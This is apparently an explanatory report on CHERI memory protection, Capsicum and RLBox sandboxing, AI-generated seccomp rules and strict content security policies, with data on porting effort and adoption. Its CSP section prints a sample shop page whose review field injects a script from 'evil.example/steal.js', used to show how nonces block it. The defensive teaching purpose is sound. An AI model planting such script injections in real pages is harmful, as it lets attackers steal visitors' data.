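The copying function writes one letter at a time and moves the address forward after each one. The first eight letters of a 12-letter password fill addresses 1000 to 1007. The ninth would go to 1008, which is out of bounds, so the processor raises an exception instead of writing it, and the program normally stops. The variable that records whether the password was right never changes, so the attacker isn't logged in.

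An attacker can't get around this by inventing a pointer with wider bounds. *CHERI with a Linux on top* (Edge, 2025) reports on a talk by Carl Shaw of Codasip, a company that designs CHERI processors. Shaw explained that a program can create a capability only from another valid one, and that the new one can't have more rights than the original. If an attacker overwrites a stored capability with made-up values, its tag becomes invalid and the processor won't use it.

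A language model helped find CVE-2026-4747, an overflow in the FreeBSD operating system that could let an attacker take over a machine through the network. *CHERI memory safety mitigates LLM-discovered vulnerability in FreeBSD* (Davis, 2026) describes how a Cambridge researcher tested CHERI against this flaw by trying the first step of the attack on CheriBSD, the CHERI version of FreeBSD. The processor stopped the overflow before it could corrupt any memory. The operating system still shut down, so an attacker could force a reboot but not take control.

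### Memory that the program has released

Bounds don't help if a program uses memory after releasing it, because the old pointer still has a valid tag and the right bounds. CHERI systems therefore quarantine released memory, search for capabilities that still point to it, and invalidate them before anything reuses the memory.

These searches take time. CheriBSD performs them for ordinary programs but not for its own kernel, the core of the operating system. Kernels constantly allocate and release memory, and Li, Zhang and colleagues write in *Understanding the Security Impact of CHERI on the Operating System Kernel* that it is not yet clear whether a practical method exists for kernels. The searches also don't cover the stack, where functions keep their temporary variables.

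Li and colleagues studied 439 past flaws in the Linux and FreeBSD kernels. CHERI would have blocked 61% of them if it included protection for released memory, and 35% without it. For a set of Linux driver flaws, CHERI would have blocked 70% with that protection and 38% without it, while Rust would have blocked 84%.

Rust and CHERI can also work together. A mistake in an unsafe block can let an attacker write anywhere in a Rust program's memory, but a CHERI processor would still enforce each pointer's bounds. That would be useful for a program like Bun, which has thousands of unsafe blocks.

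### Protecting memory and dividing programs into compartments

CHERI can also enforce capability-based isolation by dividing a program into compartments, each with its own capabilities. For example, a desktop's image reader could have access only to the file it decodes and the memory for the finished picture.

Adding memory protection mostly means recompiling the program and fixing the parts that no longer work. Compartments take more thought, because somebody has to decide where to divide the program and what each part may access. According to Lindsay and Shaw's *Recent advances in CHERI enhancing stability, maturity, and accessibility*, adding compartments usually means changing the software's architecture.

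Dividing software into compartments takes extra work, but it can stop more attacks. *Porting Software to CHERI* (Jenkinson, 2024) estimates that memory protection would have mitigated about 46% of the past vulnerabilities in nginx, a widely used web server, and that adding compartments could raise this to 61%. Developers can also build compartments without CHERI, by using sandboxes on ordinary processors. The low porting effort that CHERI's supporters cite is for memory protection alone.

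### How much code has to change

Most of the changes correct the type of a variable. Older C code often stores a pointer in a "long", a 64-bit integer. A capability doesn't fit, so it loses its bounds and tag, and the program fails when it later uses the pointer. The usual fix is to replace "long" with "intptr_t", a type that can hold a whole capability.

| Software | Lines of code | Share changed |
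|---|---|---|
| Desktop software (X11, Qt and KDE) | About 6 million | 0.026% |
| nginx | 139,804 | About 0.1% |
| Operating system kernels and V8, Chrome's JavaScript engine | Not given | 1% to 2% |

The desktop figure is from *Assessing the Viability of an Open-Source CHERI Desktop Software Ecosystem* (Watson, Laurie and Richardson, 2021). They changed about 1,600 lines, and their whole study, including a review of past vulnerabilities, took three staff months. At the $165,000 salary Orosz used for Bun, that time would cost about $41,000, or 0.7 cents per line of the software. Model fees were 8.2 cents per line for Reboot and 31 cents for Bun. Adding CHERI's memory protection by hand in 2021 was therefore much cheaper per line than translating code into Rust with AI in 2026.

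This comparison makes CHERI look somewhat better than it should. Watson and colleagues were experts who had helped develop it, and they worked on an emulator because the hardware wasn't ready. They did only limited testing of the running programs, and some problems show up only when a program runs. They also left out the desktop's JavaScript engine because it was too large a job.

The nginx port changed 118 lines in 20 files. Jenkinson warns that testing may reveal more problems and that full protection needs further changes to how nginx manages memory. nginx takes large blocks of memory and divides them up itself. A pointer to one piece can reach the whole block unless nginx's developers add code to narrow the pointer's bounds.

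Language runtimes, the programs that run code in languages such as JavaScript and Ruby, are harder to adapt. Some generate machine code as they run, so developers have to modify them to produce CHERI's instructions. Many also store pointers in fewer bits to save memory, but CHERI makes pointers larger. The hardware can sometimes help, though. *Pitfalls in VM Implementation on CHERI* (2026), on porting the Ruby interpreter, describes how the garbage collector can use the validity tag to rule out values that aren't pointers.

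Li and colleagues report that moving the FreeBSD kernel fully to capabilities took seven months, although work on CHERI support had begun in 2013. Device drivers, which make up most of the code in a modern kernel, often needed changes to only a couple of lines each.

### What developers found difficult

A small change can still be hard to get right. In *Not quite a piece of CHERI-cake*, Alhindi and Hallett (2025) asked nine C programmers who were new to CHERI to port an 89-line program, after reading two introductory reports totalling 76 pages. They only had to change the types of five variables. The compiler gave two warnings. All nine fixed the first, but only six fixed the second and got the program running.

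Five of the nine were confident that the program would run despite the warnings, just without CHERI's protection, but it would have failed. Changing the variable's type in one function made the second warning disappear, yet the program stayed broken until the programmer changed every function that used the variable.

The nine participants also reviewed four changes that other people had proposed. They accepted the three sound changes in only 13 of 27 cases, and two participants accepted the faulty one. These numbers are rough because the sample is small, but they suggest a shortage of people who understand CHERI rather than of people to type the changes.

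The UK's Defence Science and Technology Laboratory ran a larger test, in which 15 teams from industry and academia ported defense software over 12 months. They used Morello, an experimental CHERI processor made by Arm.

| What the evaluation identified | Types |
|---|---|
| Six blockers | Dependencies on other software, the need for specialist knowledge, missing utilities, performance, an unstable platform, technical debt |
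| Three enablers | Help from tools, improved code quality, trivial code porting |
| Five possible new weaknesses if CHERI is badly configured | State leaks, memory leaks, use of released memory, unsafe defaults, unstable development tools |

Agents could help with several of these blockers, for example by porting the outside libraries a program depends on or writing missing utilities, but this wouldn't fix a slow or unstable processor. The utilities matter more for CHERI than for some other hardware protections. *Should Your Database Systems Use Hardware-Assisted Memory Safety Extensions in Production?* explains that CHERI changes machine instructions throughout a program, so even debuggers need new versions.

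Lindsay and Shaw reply that Morello was a research prototype whose tools changed constantly, and that newer designs have fixed many of its problems. They work for Codasip, which sells CHERI processor designs, but their reply is plausible for the complaints about speed and stability. It is weaker on the complaints about knowledge, because they agree that the CHERI community still has to produce more training material and documentation.

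### Porting with language models

CHERI-PIT, a tool from the US research company SIFT, uses language models to make the changes. Its first version follows a fixed procedure and gives the model 36 small examples of CHERI porting. The second version uses several agents built around Claude Code and is better at changes that span several files.

*CHERI-PIT* (Musliner, 2026) reported in March that its tool had achieved "80-100% porting success" on large applications, including nginx, the PostgreSQL and SQLite databases, PHP, Python and NASA's flight software. The porting took minutes to hours and cost almost nothing in model fees.

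The evidence for that success is that compiler warnings fell from thousands to dozens or none. Musliner gives no results from running the ported programs or testing their security. Such checks matter because participants in Alhindi and Hallett's study could silence a warning without fixing the program, and an agent that aims to remove warnings could do the same. Musliner also says that the second version is less reliable than the first, "like an optimistic intern that lies." Reboot's workers also tended to report success too early.

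Agents could not have saved much work on nginx, because human programmers had already ported it by changing 118 lines. PHP and Python are more interesting because they are language runtimes, which are hard to port. If those versions work, agents may be lowering the cost of ports that used to be expensive.

### Which CHERI processors are for sale

A company that has ported its software still needs something to run it on. At the end of 2026, the choice is small.

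| Product | What it is | Availability |
|---|---|---|
| Morello | Four-core, 2.5 GHz Arm processor | Research boards since 2022, not a commercial product |
| ICENI | Microcontroller for small devices, up to 250 MHz | First chips in March 2026, now in a distributor's catalog |
| X730 | 64-bit processor design for larger systems | For license to chip makers, with an evaluation board |
| OpenTitan Earl Grey 2 | Security chip | Still in design |

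ICENI is the CHERI chip closest to being available for manufacturers to buy and build into products. CHERIoT (2025), the project behind its design, expected mass production in 2026. CHERIoT's *ICENI on a development board* (2026), by a co-founder of the company that makes the chip, announced the first working chips in March. EPS Global's *SCI Semiconductors* lists the ICENI family, but a catalog entry doesn't show that the chips are in stock. Microcontrollers like ICENI run equipment such as industrial controllers and medical devices.

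CHERI Alliance's *X730* (2026) describes Codasip's processor as the first commercially licensable one of its kind. Customers license a design and must still have the chip made. Software developers can try it on Codasip Prime, a board with a reprogrammable chip that behaves like the X730. In April, Codasip (2026) said it would also deliver complete chips. lowRISC's *OpenTitan Earl Grey 2 to support CHERI and PQC* expects design work on the security chip to continue into the first half of 2027.

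None of these is a commercial chip for a phone, laptop or server. In April, *CHERI Adoption Programme* (Finney, 2026) put the lack of chips, including ones that can run Linux, first among five obstacles to adoption.

### What CHERI costs in speed

*Sweet or Sour CHERI* (Sun, Singer and Wang, 2025) reports tests of 20 programs on Morello. Some were hardly slower with full CHERI protection, but the worst affected took 1.65 times as long. Programs that use many pointers slowed down most, because CHERI's larger pointers fill the processor's fast caches sooner.

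Part of the slowdown arose because Arm built the prototype by adapting an existing processor and kept some components designed for 64-bit pointers. For example, the part that temporarily holds data on its way to memory became a bottleneck when it had to handle 128 bits at a time. Sun and colleagues project that modest hardware improvements could greatly reduce the slowdown.

Codasip designed the X730 for CHERI from the start, and Lindsay and Shaw give its average slowdown as 3.8%. Edge reports that CHERI adds less than 5% to the area of the processor. The tags take up one bit for every 128 bits of memory, or about 0.8%. These speed and area figures are Codasip's own, but if they hold up on finished chips, few buyers would reject CHERI for being slow.

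Software can provide similar protection on ordinary processors, but with more overhead. Fil-C, for example, is a compiler that makes C programs memory safe. *Memory Safety at Scale* (Rebert, 2026) cites estimates that programs compiled with it need up to four times as many processor cycles and perhaps three to six times as much memory.

### Why CHERI is still rare

Porting most applications to CHERI took little work even before coding agents could do it, which is strong evidence that the labor of changing code is not the main obstacle to adoption. In 2021, a company that wanted to protect its servers with CHERI could have ported a program like nginx with a few changes, but there was no commercial server chip to run it on, and there still isn't one.

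*DSIT's CHERI adoption and diffusion research* (2024), a study for the UK's technology ministry, found that many of the significant barriers to adopting CHERI are economic rather than technical. It reports that chip makers won't produce hardware that has no software, developers won't write software for hardware that doesn't exist, and most customers don't know enough about the risk to ask for either.

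In a phone, for example, CHERI would take up chip space that the maker could use for features customers notice, and each new chip takes a long and expensive design process. According to the study, adoption in phones is unlikely in the near term, but prospects are better for small embedded devices, whose processors are simpler and cheaper to design. ICENI arrived before any CHERI phone or server chip, which fits that forecast.

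The CHERI Alliance, the industry group that promotes the technology, found in its *CHERI Adoption Global Ecosystem Assessment Q1 2026* (2026) that operating systems and development tools for CHERI were improving quickly, but most organizations still relied on prototypes and early chips. It also listed skills shortages and limited commercial demand among the main barriers to adoption.

Designing a processor takes a lot of skilled labor. Codasip spent more than 40 person-years just on verifying the X730. AI might eventually make that work cheaper too, but it is a different job from porting software, and the company would still have to pay for manufacturing and find customers.

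### Could cheaper porting create demand for the chips?

The average porting figures don't show how much work is needed for the software that matters most to some buyers. A phone or server maker needs the kernel, the browser and the language runtimes ported as well as the easy applications. Unported programs can still run on a CHERI processor, but without its full protection. If a phone's JavaScript engine hasn't been ported, the phone lacks full protection in one of the places attackers are most likely to target.

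Suppose a manufacturer has to change 1% of the lines when porting 10 million lines of kernel and runtime code. At the pace of the desktop study, changing those 100,000 lines would take about 16 staff years. Difficult code would probably take several times as long, so porting could take as much labor as verifying the X730. Agents that did this work reliably would remove a substantial expense.

Agents could also help break the standoff. Developers can port and test software on an emulator before anyone makes the chip, as Watson and colleagues did. If agents made this work cheap enough, a chip maker could launch a processor with a full set of software ready. DSIT's study gives this argument some support, because it lists the cost of updating phone software as a significant barrier. Attacks that use AI could add to demand by making customers more aware of the risk.

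But even if the software were ready, the chip maker would still need customers willing to pay for security. Software has already been advancing faster than hardware, and this has not led to a server or phone chip. CHERI-PIT also has not yet shown that its ports of PHP and Python work, let alone a port of something as complex as V8.

AI could also reduce demand for CHERI by making it cheaper to rewrite C and C++ code in Rust. Rebert, who works on memory safety at Google, describes one possible future in which AI progress levels off, large-scale rewrites remain impractical, and CHERI protects old code that nobody can change. That future has become less likely since Rebert's talk in April 2026, because AI agents have moved Bun and GitHub's Copilot runtime to Rust.

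In the other future, where most software gets rewritten, Rebert still sees uses for CHERI in firmware, in the remaining C and C++, and in engines such as V8. Rewriting V8 in Rust would not solve all its memory problems, because V8 generates machine code that can contain errors Rust's compiler can't check for. Shaw finds compartments more interesting than memory safety, since no current language provides them. These uses are narrower than protecting all old C code, and a chip maker would have to decide whether they justify the cost of a new processor.

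## Capsicum and RLBox: dividing programs into sandboxes

CHERI's compartments need a new processor, but developers can divide a program into sandboxes on ordinary machines. Capsicum does this through the operating system and RLBox through the compiler. Sandboxing some programs takes only a few new lines of code. Even so, *Playing in the Sandbox* (Alhindi and Hallett, 2025) cites a survey in which fewer than 1% of software packages set up a sandbox in their own code. The survey leaves out programs that an administrator sandboxes from outside.

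### Capsicum: giving up access

*Capsicum* (Watson, Anderson and colleagues, 2010) presented an extension to FreeBSD that lets a program give up most of the access it gets from its user.

The program first opens the files and connections it needs, then calls the function cap_enter, which puts it in capability mode. From then on, the operating system refuses requests to open anything by its file path or network address. The program can't leave capability mode, and neither can any program it starts. The program keeps the handles to whatever it opened earlier, and these handles are its capabilities.

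Developers can restrict each handle to a chosen set of about 60 available rights, such as reading or writing. A handle to a folder lets the program open files inside that folder but not follow a path out of it.

tcpdump, which prints network traffic, suits this design because it opens its data source at the start and then runs in a loop. Watson and colleagues put it in capability mode with two lines of code. They then noticed that it could still read what the user typed, and blocking that brought the total to about ten lines. The change also broke the feature that looks up the names of network addresses. The code for this opens a settings file only when it first needs one, and by then tcpdump had given up access to files. They fixed it by sending the lookups to a separate service.

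gzip, which compresses files, took 409 lines, or 16% more code. The main program opens the files and passes two handles to a sandboxed process that does the compression. At first, the sandboxed version seemed faster than the original. It turned out that the developers had forgotten to pass the user's chosen compression level into the sandbox, so gzip was doing the wrong job. The compiler gave no warning. The correct version adds about 2.4 milliseconds per run.

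Sandboxing Chromium with Capsicum took only about 100 lines of code, in a program of 4.3 million, because Google had already divided the browser into separate processes. Watson and colleagues compared this with the amount of code that Chromium's other sandboxes needed at the time.

| Operating system | Sandboxing method | Lines of code in 2010 |
|---|---|---|
| Windows | Access control lists | 22,350 |
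| Linux | seccomp | 11,301 |
| Linux | chroot | 605 |
| Mac OS X | Seatbelt | 560 |
| Linux | SELinux | 200 |
| FreeBSD | Capsicum | 100 |

A sandbox that takes little code isn't necessarily a strong one. The SELinux rules took 200 lines, but they let every sandboxed process read all the files in the system's settings folder. The table also shows the limits of good support on one operating system. A browser maker that wants to protect all its users has to build and maintain a different sandbox for each system.

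### RLBox: checking what a library returns

Browsers rely on dozens of outside libraries to handle images, sound and fonts. The traditional way to isolate a library is to run it in its own process. Mozilla, which develops Firefox, wrote in *WebAssembly and Back Again* (2021) that this usually takes a lot of restructuring and that every process uses extra memory.

RLBox keeps the library in the same process. Firefox's build system compiles the library into WebAssembly, a format that limits code to a fixed region of memory. It then translates the WebAssembly back into C and builds it into the browser. The library's source code stays the same.

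The browser still has to use what the library returns, and an attacker who controls the library can return anything. RLBox therefore marks every value from the sandbox as "tainted". The browser can add two tainted numbers, for example, but the sum is tainted too. The compiler rejects code that bases a decision on a tainted value until the programmer adds a check.

Narayan, Disselkoen and colleagues (2020), in *Retrofitting Fine Grain Isolation in the Firefox Renderer*, recorded the work of adapting Firefox to six sandboxed libraries.

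| What the library decodes | Lines added to Firefox | Different checks written | Working days |
|---|---|---|---|
| JPEG images | 338 | 11 | Not recorded |
| PNG images | 470 | 14 | Not recorded |
| Compressed web pages | 108 | 3 | 1 |
| Theora video | 77 | 3 | 3 |
| VPX video | 82 | 2 | 3 |
| Vorbis audio | 67 | 2 | 2 |

Sandboxing a library took two and a quarter days on average, which would cost about $1,400 at the salary used for Bun. This average excludes the image decoders, which needed the most code and the most checks, because the researchers adapted them while still building RLBox. So experts could already sandbox a library by hand in 2020 for roughly what Reboot later spent on model fees to translate a small program.

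In the research version, web pages took 3% longer to load, and Firefox's peak memory use rose by 25% while it decoded content. With separate processes, pages took 13% longer to load. Other programs can slow down more. Sandboxing a text-formatting library in the Apache web server took the researchers one day and reduced the number of requests the server handled per second by 27%.

### Example: sandboxing an image decoder

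Suppose a website lets users upload profile photos. A single C++ program receives each photo, decodes it with the C library libjpeg, shrinks it and saves it. The program also holds the password to the user database, so an attacker who exploits a flaw in libjpeg can steal the password. The table adapts the steps that Narayan and colleagues followed to sandbox libjpeg in Firefox.

| Step | What the developer does | Type of work |
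|---|---|---|
| Choose the boundary | Puts libjpeg in the sandbox and leaves the database code outside | Judgment |
| Redirect the calls | Calls libjpeg through RLBox, with isolation still switched off so that the program keeps working | Mechanical |
| Move shared data | Puts the data that both sides use in the sandbox's memory, guided by compiler errors | Mechanical |
| Check the results | Writes a check for each returned value that could do harm | Judgment |
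| Limit callbacks | Decides which of the program's functions libjpeg may call, and when | Judgment |
| Switch on isolation | Replaces the ordinary libjpeg with the WebAssembly version | Mechanical |

The developer must also choose how many sandboxes to use. If all uploads share one, an attacker's photo could take over the decoder and then copy or alter the next user's photo. Creating a new sandbox for every photo prevents this. In the research version, each sandbox took about a millisecond to create and used 1.6 MB of memory. Narayan and colleagues found that a sandbox per image added too much overhead for Firefox, but the overhead would probably be acceptable for a website that only decodes new uploads.

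Different libraries shouldn't share a sandbox. If they did, a malicious sound file in a browser could take over the library that unpacks web pages and change the pages' scripts. Some parts of a program aren't worth sandboxing. Confining the JavaScript engine, for example, achieves little because an attacker who controls it can already do anything the page can do.

The program must check the row number that libjpeg returns, but not the pixels, because any pixel value is a valid color and the worst result is a wrong picture. Suppose a photo has 100 rows of 400 bytes, so the program reserves 40,000 bytes. To find where a row belongs, it multiplies the row number by 400. If a hijacked libjpeg returns row 5,000 and the program doesn't check it, the program itself writes outside the sandbox, about two million bytes past the end of the memory it reserved.

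A one-line check can reject any row number outside 0 to 99. The limit has to come from the program's own record of how much memory it reserved, since a hijacked libjpeg could falsify the photo's height too. The program must also copy the row number before checking it, because libjpeg could otherwise change the number between the check and the write.

Another risk comes from callbacks, which are the program's own functions that libjpeg can call. When a file is damaged, libjpeg calls an error function that jumps back to a saved place in the program. If a hijacked libjpeg calls this function before the program has saved a place, the attacker may be able to choose where the program goes next. The developer should let libjpeg call the function only after the program has saved that place.

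RLBox's compiler errors show where checks are missing, but not whether a check is correct. Narayan and colleagues found that writing the checks was the hardest part, even though most were two to four lines long.

### Can language models make these decisions?

No one seems to have published measurements of how well language models choose where to divide an ordinary C or C++ program. *Towards Secure Program Partitioning for Smart Contracts with LLM's In-Context Learning* (2025) uses a language model to divide smart contracts. These are usually short programs that run on a blockchain, so the results are weak evidence of how well a model would divide a browser or a web server.

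*Compartmentalization-Aware Automated Program Repair* (Hu, Sun and Olivier, 2026) reports a small experiment on the checks. The researchers put an Apache add-on in a sandbox and had it return an invalid pointer, which crashed the server. The server should check the pointer before using it, but GPT-5 put the check in the preferred place in only two of ten attempts. In five, it put the check inside the sandbox, where an attacker could skip it.

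When the researchers' system specified which side to trust and traced the bad data, the model chose the right place for the fix all ten times. But a person had supplied the division and the trust rules, so the result doesn't show that a model can work those out. It also covers only one flaw, and today's models are much stronger than GPT-5. Even the better fix assumed that the server could reliably check whether a pointer was valid.

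### AI-written permission rules

Researchers have done more work on seccomp, a Linux feature that limits which system calls a program may make. System calls are requests to the operating system, such as to open a file or start another program. Linux has more than 450 of them, and most programs need far fewer.

In *Hybrid Seccomp Profiling with LLM Assistance for Container Security*, Ahn, Kim and colleagues (2026) had a language model write thousands of test programs for five common server applications, then ran the tests and recorded every system call. The table compares the results with Confine, an older tool that analyzes code without running it, and with a partly manual analysis of which calls each application needs.

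| Application | Calls needed, by partly manual analysis | Calls Confine allows | Calls recorded in the AI-written tests |
|---|---|---|---|
| Redis | 80 | 206 | 67 |
| nginx | 99 | 256 | 71 |
| Memcached | 81 | 246 | 44 |
| Apache | 56 | 236 | 56 |
| PostgreSQL | 100 | 252 | 92 |

Rules based only on the AI-written tests would be much tighter than Confine's, but probably too tight. If the manual analysis is right, they would block at least 13 calls that Redis might need and at least 37 that Memcached might need. The application could fail the first time it did something the tests hadn't covered. The tests also found a few calls that the older tools had missed. Ahn and colleagues therefore plan to allow the calls found by either method and raise an alarm if the application often uses calls that the tests never triggered.

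A similar system by Vo and Liljestrand (2026), in *AI-assisted sandboxing container policy generation*, blocked 24 of 25 attack patterns each for PostgreSQL and Elasticsearch, and all 20 for Memcached. They planned to check whether the applications still worked under the rules, but gave no results. Their rules allow 155 calls for PostgreSQL and 63 for Memcached, well above the numbers Ahn and colleagues recorded. The setups differed, but the gap suggests that the rules depend heavily on which tests the model writes.

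Alhindi and Hallett gave seven developers with seccomp experience an hour to write such rules for a 115-line program. Six succeeded, and all six sandboxes were different, allowing between 9 and 27 calls. One developer asked ChatGPT to write the rules from a recording of the program's calls. ChatGPT's first version allowed everything. A later version stopped the program when it tried to rename a full log file, which hadn't happened during the recording. The developer finished with 26 allowed calls, including one that would let an attacker start other programs, and took longer than anyone else who succeeded.

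This was one person using a chatbot. A coding agent could have run the program for longer and found the missing call. But it would have had less reason to remove the unnecessary permissions, because the program works just as well with them. People make this mistake too. The developer who wrote the loosest rules, with 27 calls, wrote them by hand.

There is less evidence for other kinds of rules. Sha, Liu and colleagues (2024) reported in *Automatic generation of AppArmor security policies based on large language models* that their AI-written AppArmor rules didn't interfere with the application's normal operation. *KubeGuard* (2025) uses models to suggest tighter settings for Kubernetes, a system that manages containers, but people decide whether to apply them. There seem to be no comparable results for SELinux rules written by language models.

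*Reparo* (2026) tested models on a related task, writing policies that set who may do what within an application, for 228 software projects. After automatic repair, 88% to 92% of one small model's policies were valid, depending on the policy language, compared with 40% to 92% for another small model. A valid policy follows the rules of its language but can still give access to the wrong person.

### Why sandboxes are still uncommon

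Writing the code was rarely the main obstacle. Two lines were enough to put tcpdump in capability mode, and most of the libraries in the RLBox study took three days or less to sandbox. If labor were all that mattered, Firefox would probably sandbox many more libraries by now. In 2021, Mozilla was isolating five and had identified "a number of other good candidates." Its current documentation, *RLBox sandboxing*, lists six: Graphite, Ogg, Hunspell, Expat, WOFF2 and SoundTouch. They handle fonts, sound, spelling and XML, and none decodes images.

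Mozilla said some libraries are unsuitable for sandboxing because they share too much memory with the rest of the browser or because they can't be allowed to run more slowly. The second reason may apply to image decoders, since most JPEG images took 23% to 32% longer to decode in the research version. Speed also mattered at Google, which stopped sandboxing its GIF decoder after rewriting it in Rust.

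How tightly a program is sandboxed also depends on the operating system. Alhindi and Hallett point out that OpenBSD sandboxes the compression program xz by default, using a simple feature called Pledge. Linux restricts xz less, although its seccomp feature is more powerful. They think seccomp's power is part of the problem, because it leaves developers with so many decisions.

Upkeep discourages developers from making sandboxes strict. Several developers in the study avoided detailed rules because a later change to the program could break them. *SysComb* (2026) reports that most applications in production set an overly permissive filter when they start and rarely change it afterward. Firefox's sandboxes also create maintenance work that is easy to miss. Some versions of Firefox are built without the sandboxes, and in those versions, code that would be safe inside a sandbox can let one copy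 of a library interfere with another. Mozilla warns its developers not to rely on tests to find this mistake, because its automatic tests don't cover those versions.

Labor does explain some choices. Mozilla began by sandboxing Graphite, a font library, because rewriting and maintaining such specialized code was "not an ideal use of our limited engineering resources." Agents have made that kind of rewrite cheaper, which may reduce the need for some sandboxes. One developer in Alhindi and Hallett's study could have used a stricter sandbox by reorganizing the program to open its files first, but didn't, despite having about half an hour left. "I don't want to modify my entire program," the developer said. An agent could also make that change cheaply, but someone would still have to decide what the program should be allowed to do once its files were open.

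## Strict content security policy on websites

Browsers can already enforce a content security policy (CSP). To use one, a website sends one extra line with each page and adapts its own scripts. About a fifth of sites now send a policy, but very few send a strict one.

### How the browser blocks an injected script

This short page from an online shop shows a button and an unfiltered customer review that contains an attacker's script.

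```html
<p>Great kettle! <script src="https://evil.example/steal.js"></script></p>
<button onclick="addToCart(42)">Add to cart</button>
<script>
  function addToCart(id) { fetch("/cart/" + id, { method: "POST" }); }
</script>
```

Without a policy, the browser downloads steal.js and runs it just as it runs the shop's own script. The shop can prevent this by sending the following line with the page:

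```
Content-Security-Policy: script-src 'nonce-Zk3vQ9xT' 'strict-dynamic'; object-src 'none'; base-uri 'none'
```

The browser runs a script in the page only if the script's tag contains the nonce. Real nonces are longer, and the server generates a new one each time it sends the page. The attacker wrote the review before the server generated the nonce, so the attacker's tag can't contain it, and the browser doesn't load steal.js.

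The keyword 'strict-dynamic' lets a script the browser has already approved add other scripts that have no nonce. An analytics script, for example, may fetch several more while it runs, from addresses the shop doesn't know in advance.

The last two rules block plug-ins, which can run their own scripts, and tags that change where the page's relative addresses lead. Under Chromium's *Web Mitigation Metrics*, a policy meets the basic standard only if it restricts scripts, plug-ins and these tags.

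### Adapting the shop's own code

This policy also breaks the shop's page. The shop's script has no nonce, so the browser blocks it. The button's "onclick" attribute is an inline event handler, and a nonce can't approve one of those. The developer has to change both:

```html
<p>Great kettle! <script src="https://evil.example/steal.js"></script></p>
<button id="add">Add to cart</button>
<script nonce="Zk3vQ9xT">
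  function addToCart(id) { fetch("/cart/" + id, { method: "POST" }); }
  document.getElementById("add")
    .addEventListener("click", () => addToCart(42));
</script>
```

The server's page template can fill in the nonce automatically. The button now has a name instead of a handler, and the approved script uses that name to attach the click action. The attacker's tag is still in the page, but the browser ignores it.

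Neither change is difficult, but some handlers on an old site may be hard to find because the site's code builds them from pieces of text.

### Policies that don't stop attacks

A developer can also make the button work again by adding 'unsafe-inline' to a policy that has no nonce. The browser then runs every inline script and handler, including an attacker's, so the policy gives almost no protection against XSS. If the policy contains a nonce, modern browsers ignore 'unsafe-inline'. Some sites include both so very old browsers can still run their scripts.

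The older way to approve scripts is to list the domains they may come from. But many domains host a service that returns a script beginning with whatever function name the request contains. If the service doesn't restrict that name, an attacker can put a whole program in its place, and the browser will run it because it comes from an approved domain.

Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues (2016), in *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!*, found unsafe services or libraries on 14 of the 15 domains that sites most often approved for scripts. They collected 26,011 different policies from Google's search index and concluded that attackers could bypass 94.72% of them. In response, they proposed 'strict-dynamic', which makes the browser ignore the list of domains and rely on nonces or hashes.

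Long lists are also hard to keep correct. *Complex Security Policy?* (Roth, Barron et al., 2020) tracked the policies of 10,000 popular websites from 2012 to 2018, using archived copies of the sites. Of 373 sites that approved scripts by domain, 50 had at some point approved a domain that an attacker might have been able to exploit. For example, the credit-reporting company Experian approved a misspelled domain for seven months. Whoever owned that domain could have supplied scripts to Experian's pages.

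Golinelli, Bonomi and Crispo (2023) found that 598 of 2,271 sites with nonce-based policies sent the same nonce more than once. An attacker may be able to read a reused nonce from one copy of the page and put it in a script that another visitor's browser will accept.

### How many sites have a strict policy?

Weissbacher and colleagues found in 2014 that only 1% of the 100 most popular sites used a content security policy. *Fetch Me If You Can* (2026) notes that their study followed the top million sites for 16 months and found just 815 that enforced one.

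HTTP Archive's *Security*, a chapter of its 2025 Web Almanac, and Helme's *Top 1 Million Analysis June 2026* (2026) show how much has changed. Helme crawled the top million sites and got responses from 819,002. The table gives each survey's figures as a share of all the sites it examined.

| Survey | Any policy | Policy with a nonce | Policy with 'strict-dynamic' |
|---|---|---|---|
| Roth and colleagues, 2018 | 10.3% | 0.24% | 0.08% |
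| HTTP Archive, 2025 | 21.9% | At most 4.4% | At most 2.2% |
| Helme, June 2026 | 20.8% | 5.1% | 0.3% |

The surveys cover different sites, so the rows don't form a precise trend. HTTP Archive reports nonces and 'strict-dynamic' as shares of the policies that control scripts, so its figures here are upper limits. All three surveys looked mainly at homepages, and Helme notes that some sites send a policy only on sensitive pages, such as payment pages. Helme runs Report URI, which sells CSP monitoring.

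Many policies aren't meant to stop XSS. Of the 1,032 sites in the 2020 study that enforced a policy at the end of 2018, only 421 tried to control scripts. Others used CSP to force encrypted connections or to stop other sites from displaying their pages inside a frame. These uses need little or no change to a site's scripts, and they are much more widely used than strict policies.

Most of the sites that tried to control scripts used 'unsafe-inline' without a nonce. In December 2018, 378 sites did this, and 180 of them had inline event handlers on their homepages. Some of the other 198 probably had handlers on other pages, but many may have mainly needed to add nonces to their script tags. If labor had been the only obstacle, more of these sites should have had strict policies.

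Sites that rely on lists have to keep updating them. The rental site Airbnb began testing a policy in November 2014 and changed its enforced policy 222 times between May 2015 and December 2017, adding and removing hashes as its scripts changed. Throughout that period, the policy also allowed scripts from any encrypted web address, so the updates added little protection. Airbnb enforced a limited list of domains in March 2018. A nonce doesn't depend on a script's content, so it would have made most of those updates unnecessary.

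### How Twitter and Dropbox adopted CSP

In 2013, Twitter had a content security policy (CSP) on its mobile site, its advertising site and several others, but not on twitter.com. The main site was one of the company's oldest projects and contained "a wealth of inline JavaScript." Twitter had banned new inline scripts across the company, and every web development team took part in the move to CSP.

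This supports the labor explanation, since Twitter wanted the protection but was waiting for its developers to clean up old code. Twitter also needed a rule that every team had to follow, because otherwise developers might have added inline scripts as fast as others removed them.

Report URI's *Twitter said their own site was too old for CSP* reproduces much of the policy that the site, now x.com, sends today. The policy contains a fresh nonce and forbids inline event handlers. Report URI says that an injected script can't run, wherever it comes from. But the policy it prints also allows scripts from Twitter's own domains and has no 'strict-dynamic', so browsers would still accept a script from those domains without a nonce. The policy is much stronger than having no policy, but it isn't strict in the sense used here.

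Dropbox, the file-storage company, automated much of the conversion without AI. Akhawe (2015), in *[CSP] Unsafe-inline and nonce deployment*, describes how its engineers changed the template system to put a nonce on every script tag. They also wrote code that turned each old inline handler into a small approved script, much like the change to the shop's button. Dropbox had already stopped using inline handlers in new code.

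If the site inserts an attacker's text into one of its own handlers, automatic conversion also approves the attacker's code. Akhawe accepted this risk because Dropbox's templates were good at filtering such text.

Checking the result took longer. Dropbox used CSP's report-only mode, in which the browser runs everything but reports what the policy would have blocked. The nonce policy stayed in this mode for nearly a month while engineers found and fixed violations, which Akhawe calls "a tedious process." Dropbox's original policy, which listed approved domains, had spent months in report-only mode.

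Many of the reports had nothing to do with Dropbox's code. Akhawe's *[CSP] On Reporting and Filtering* (2015) explains that browser extensions add their own scripts to pages, and each one can trigger a report. The engineers had to build filters before the reports were useful.

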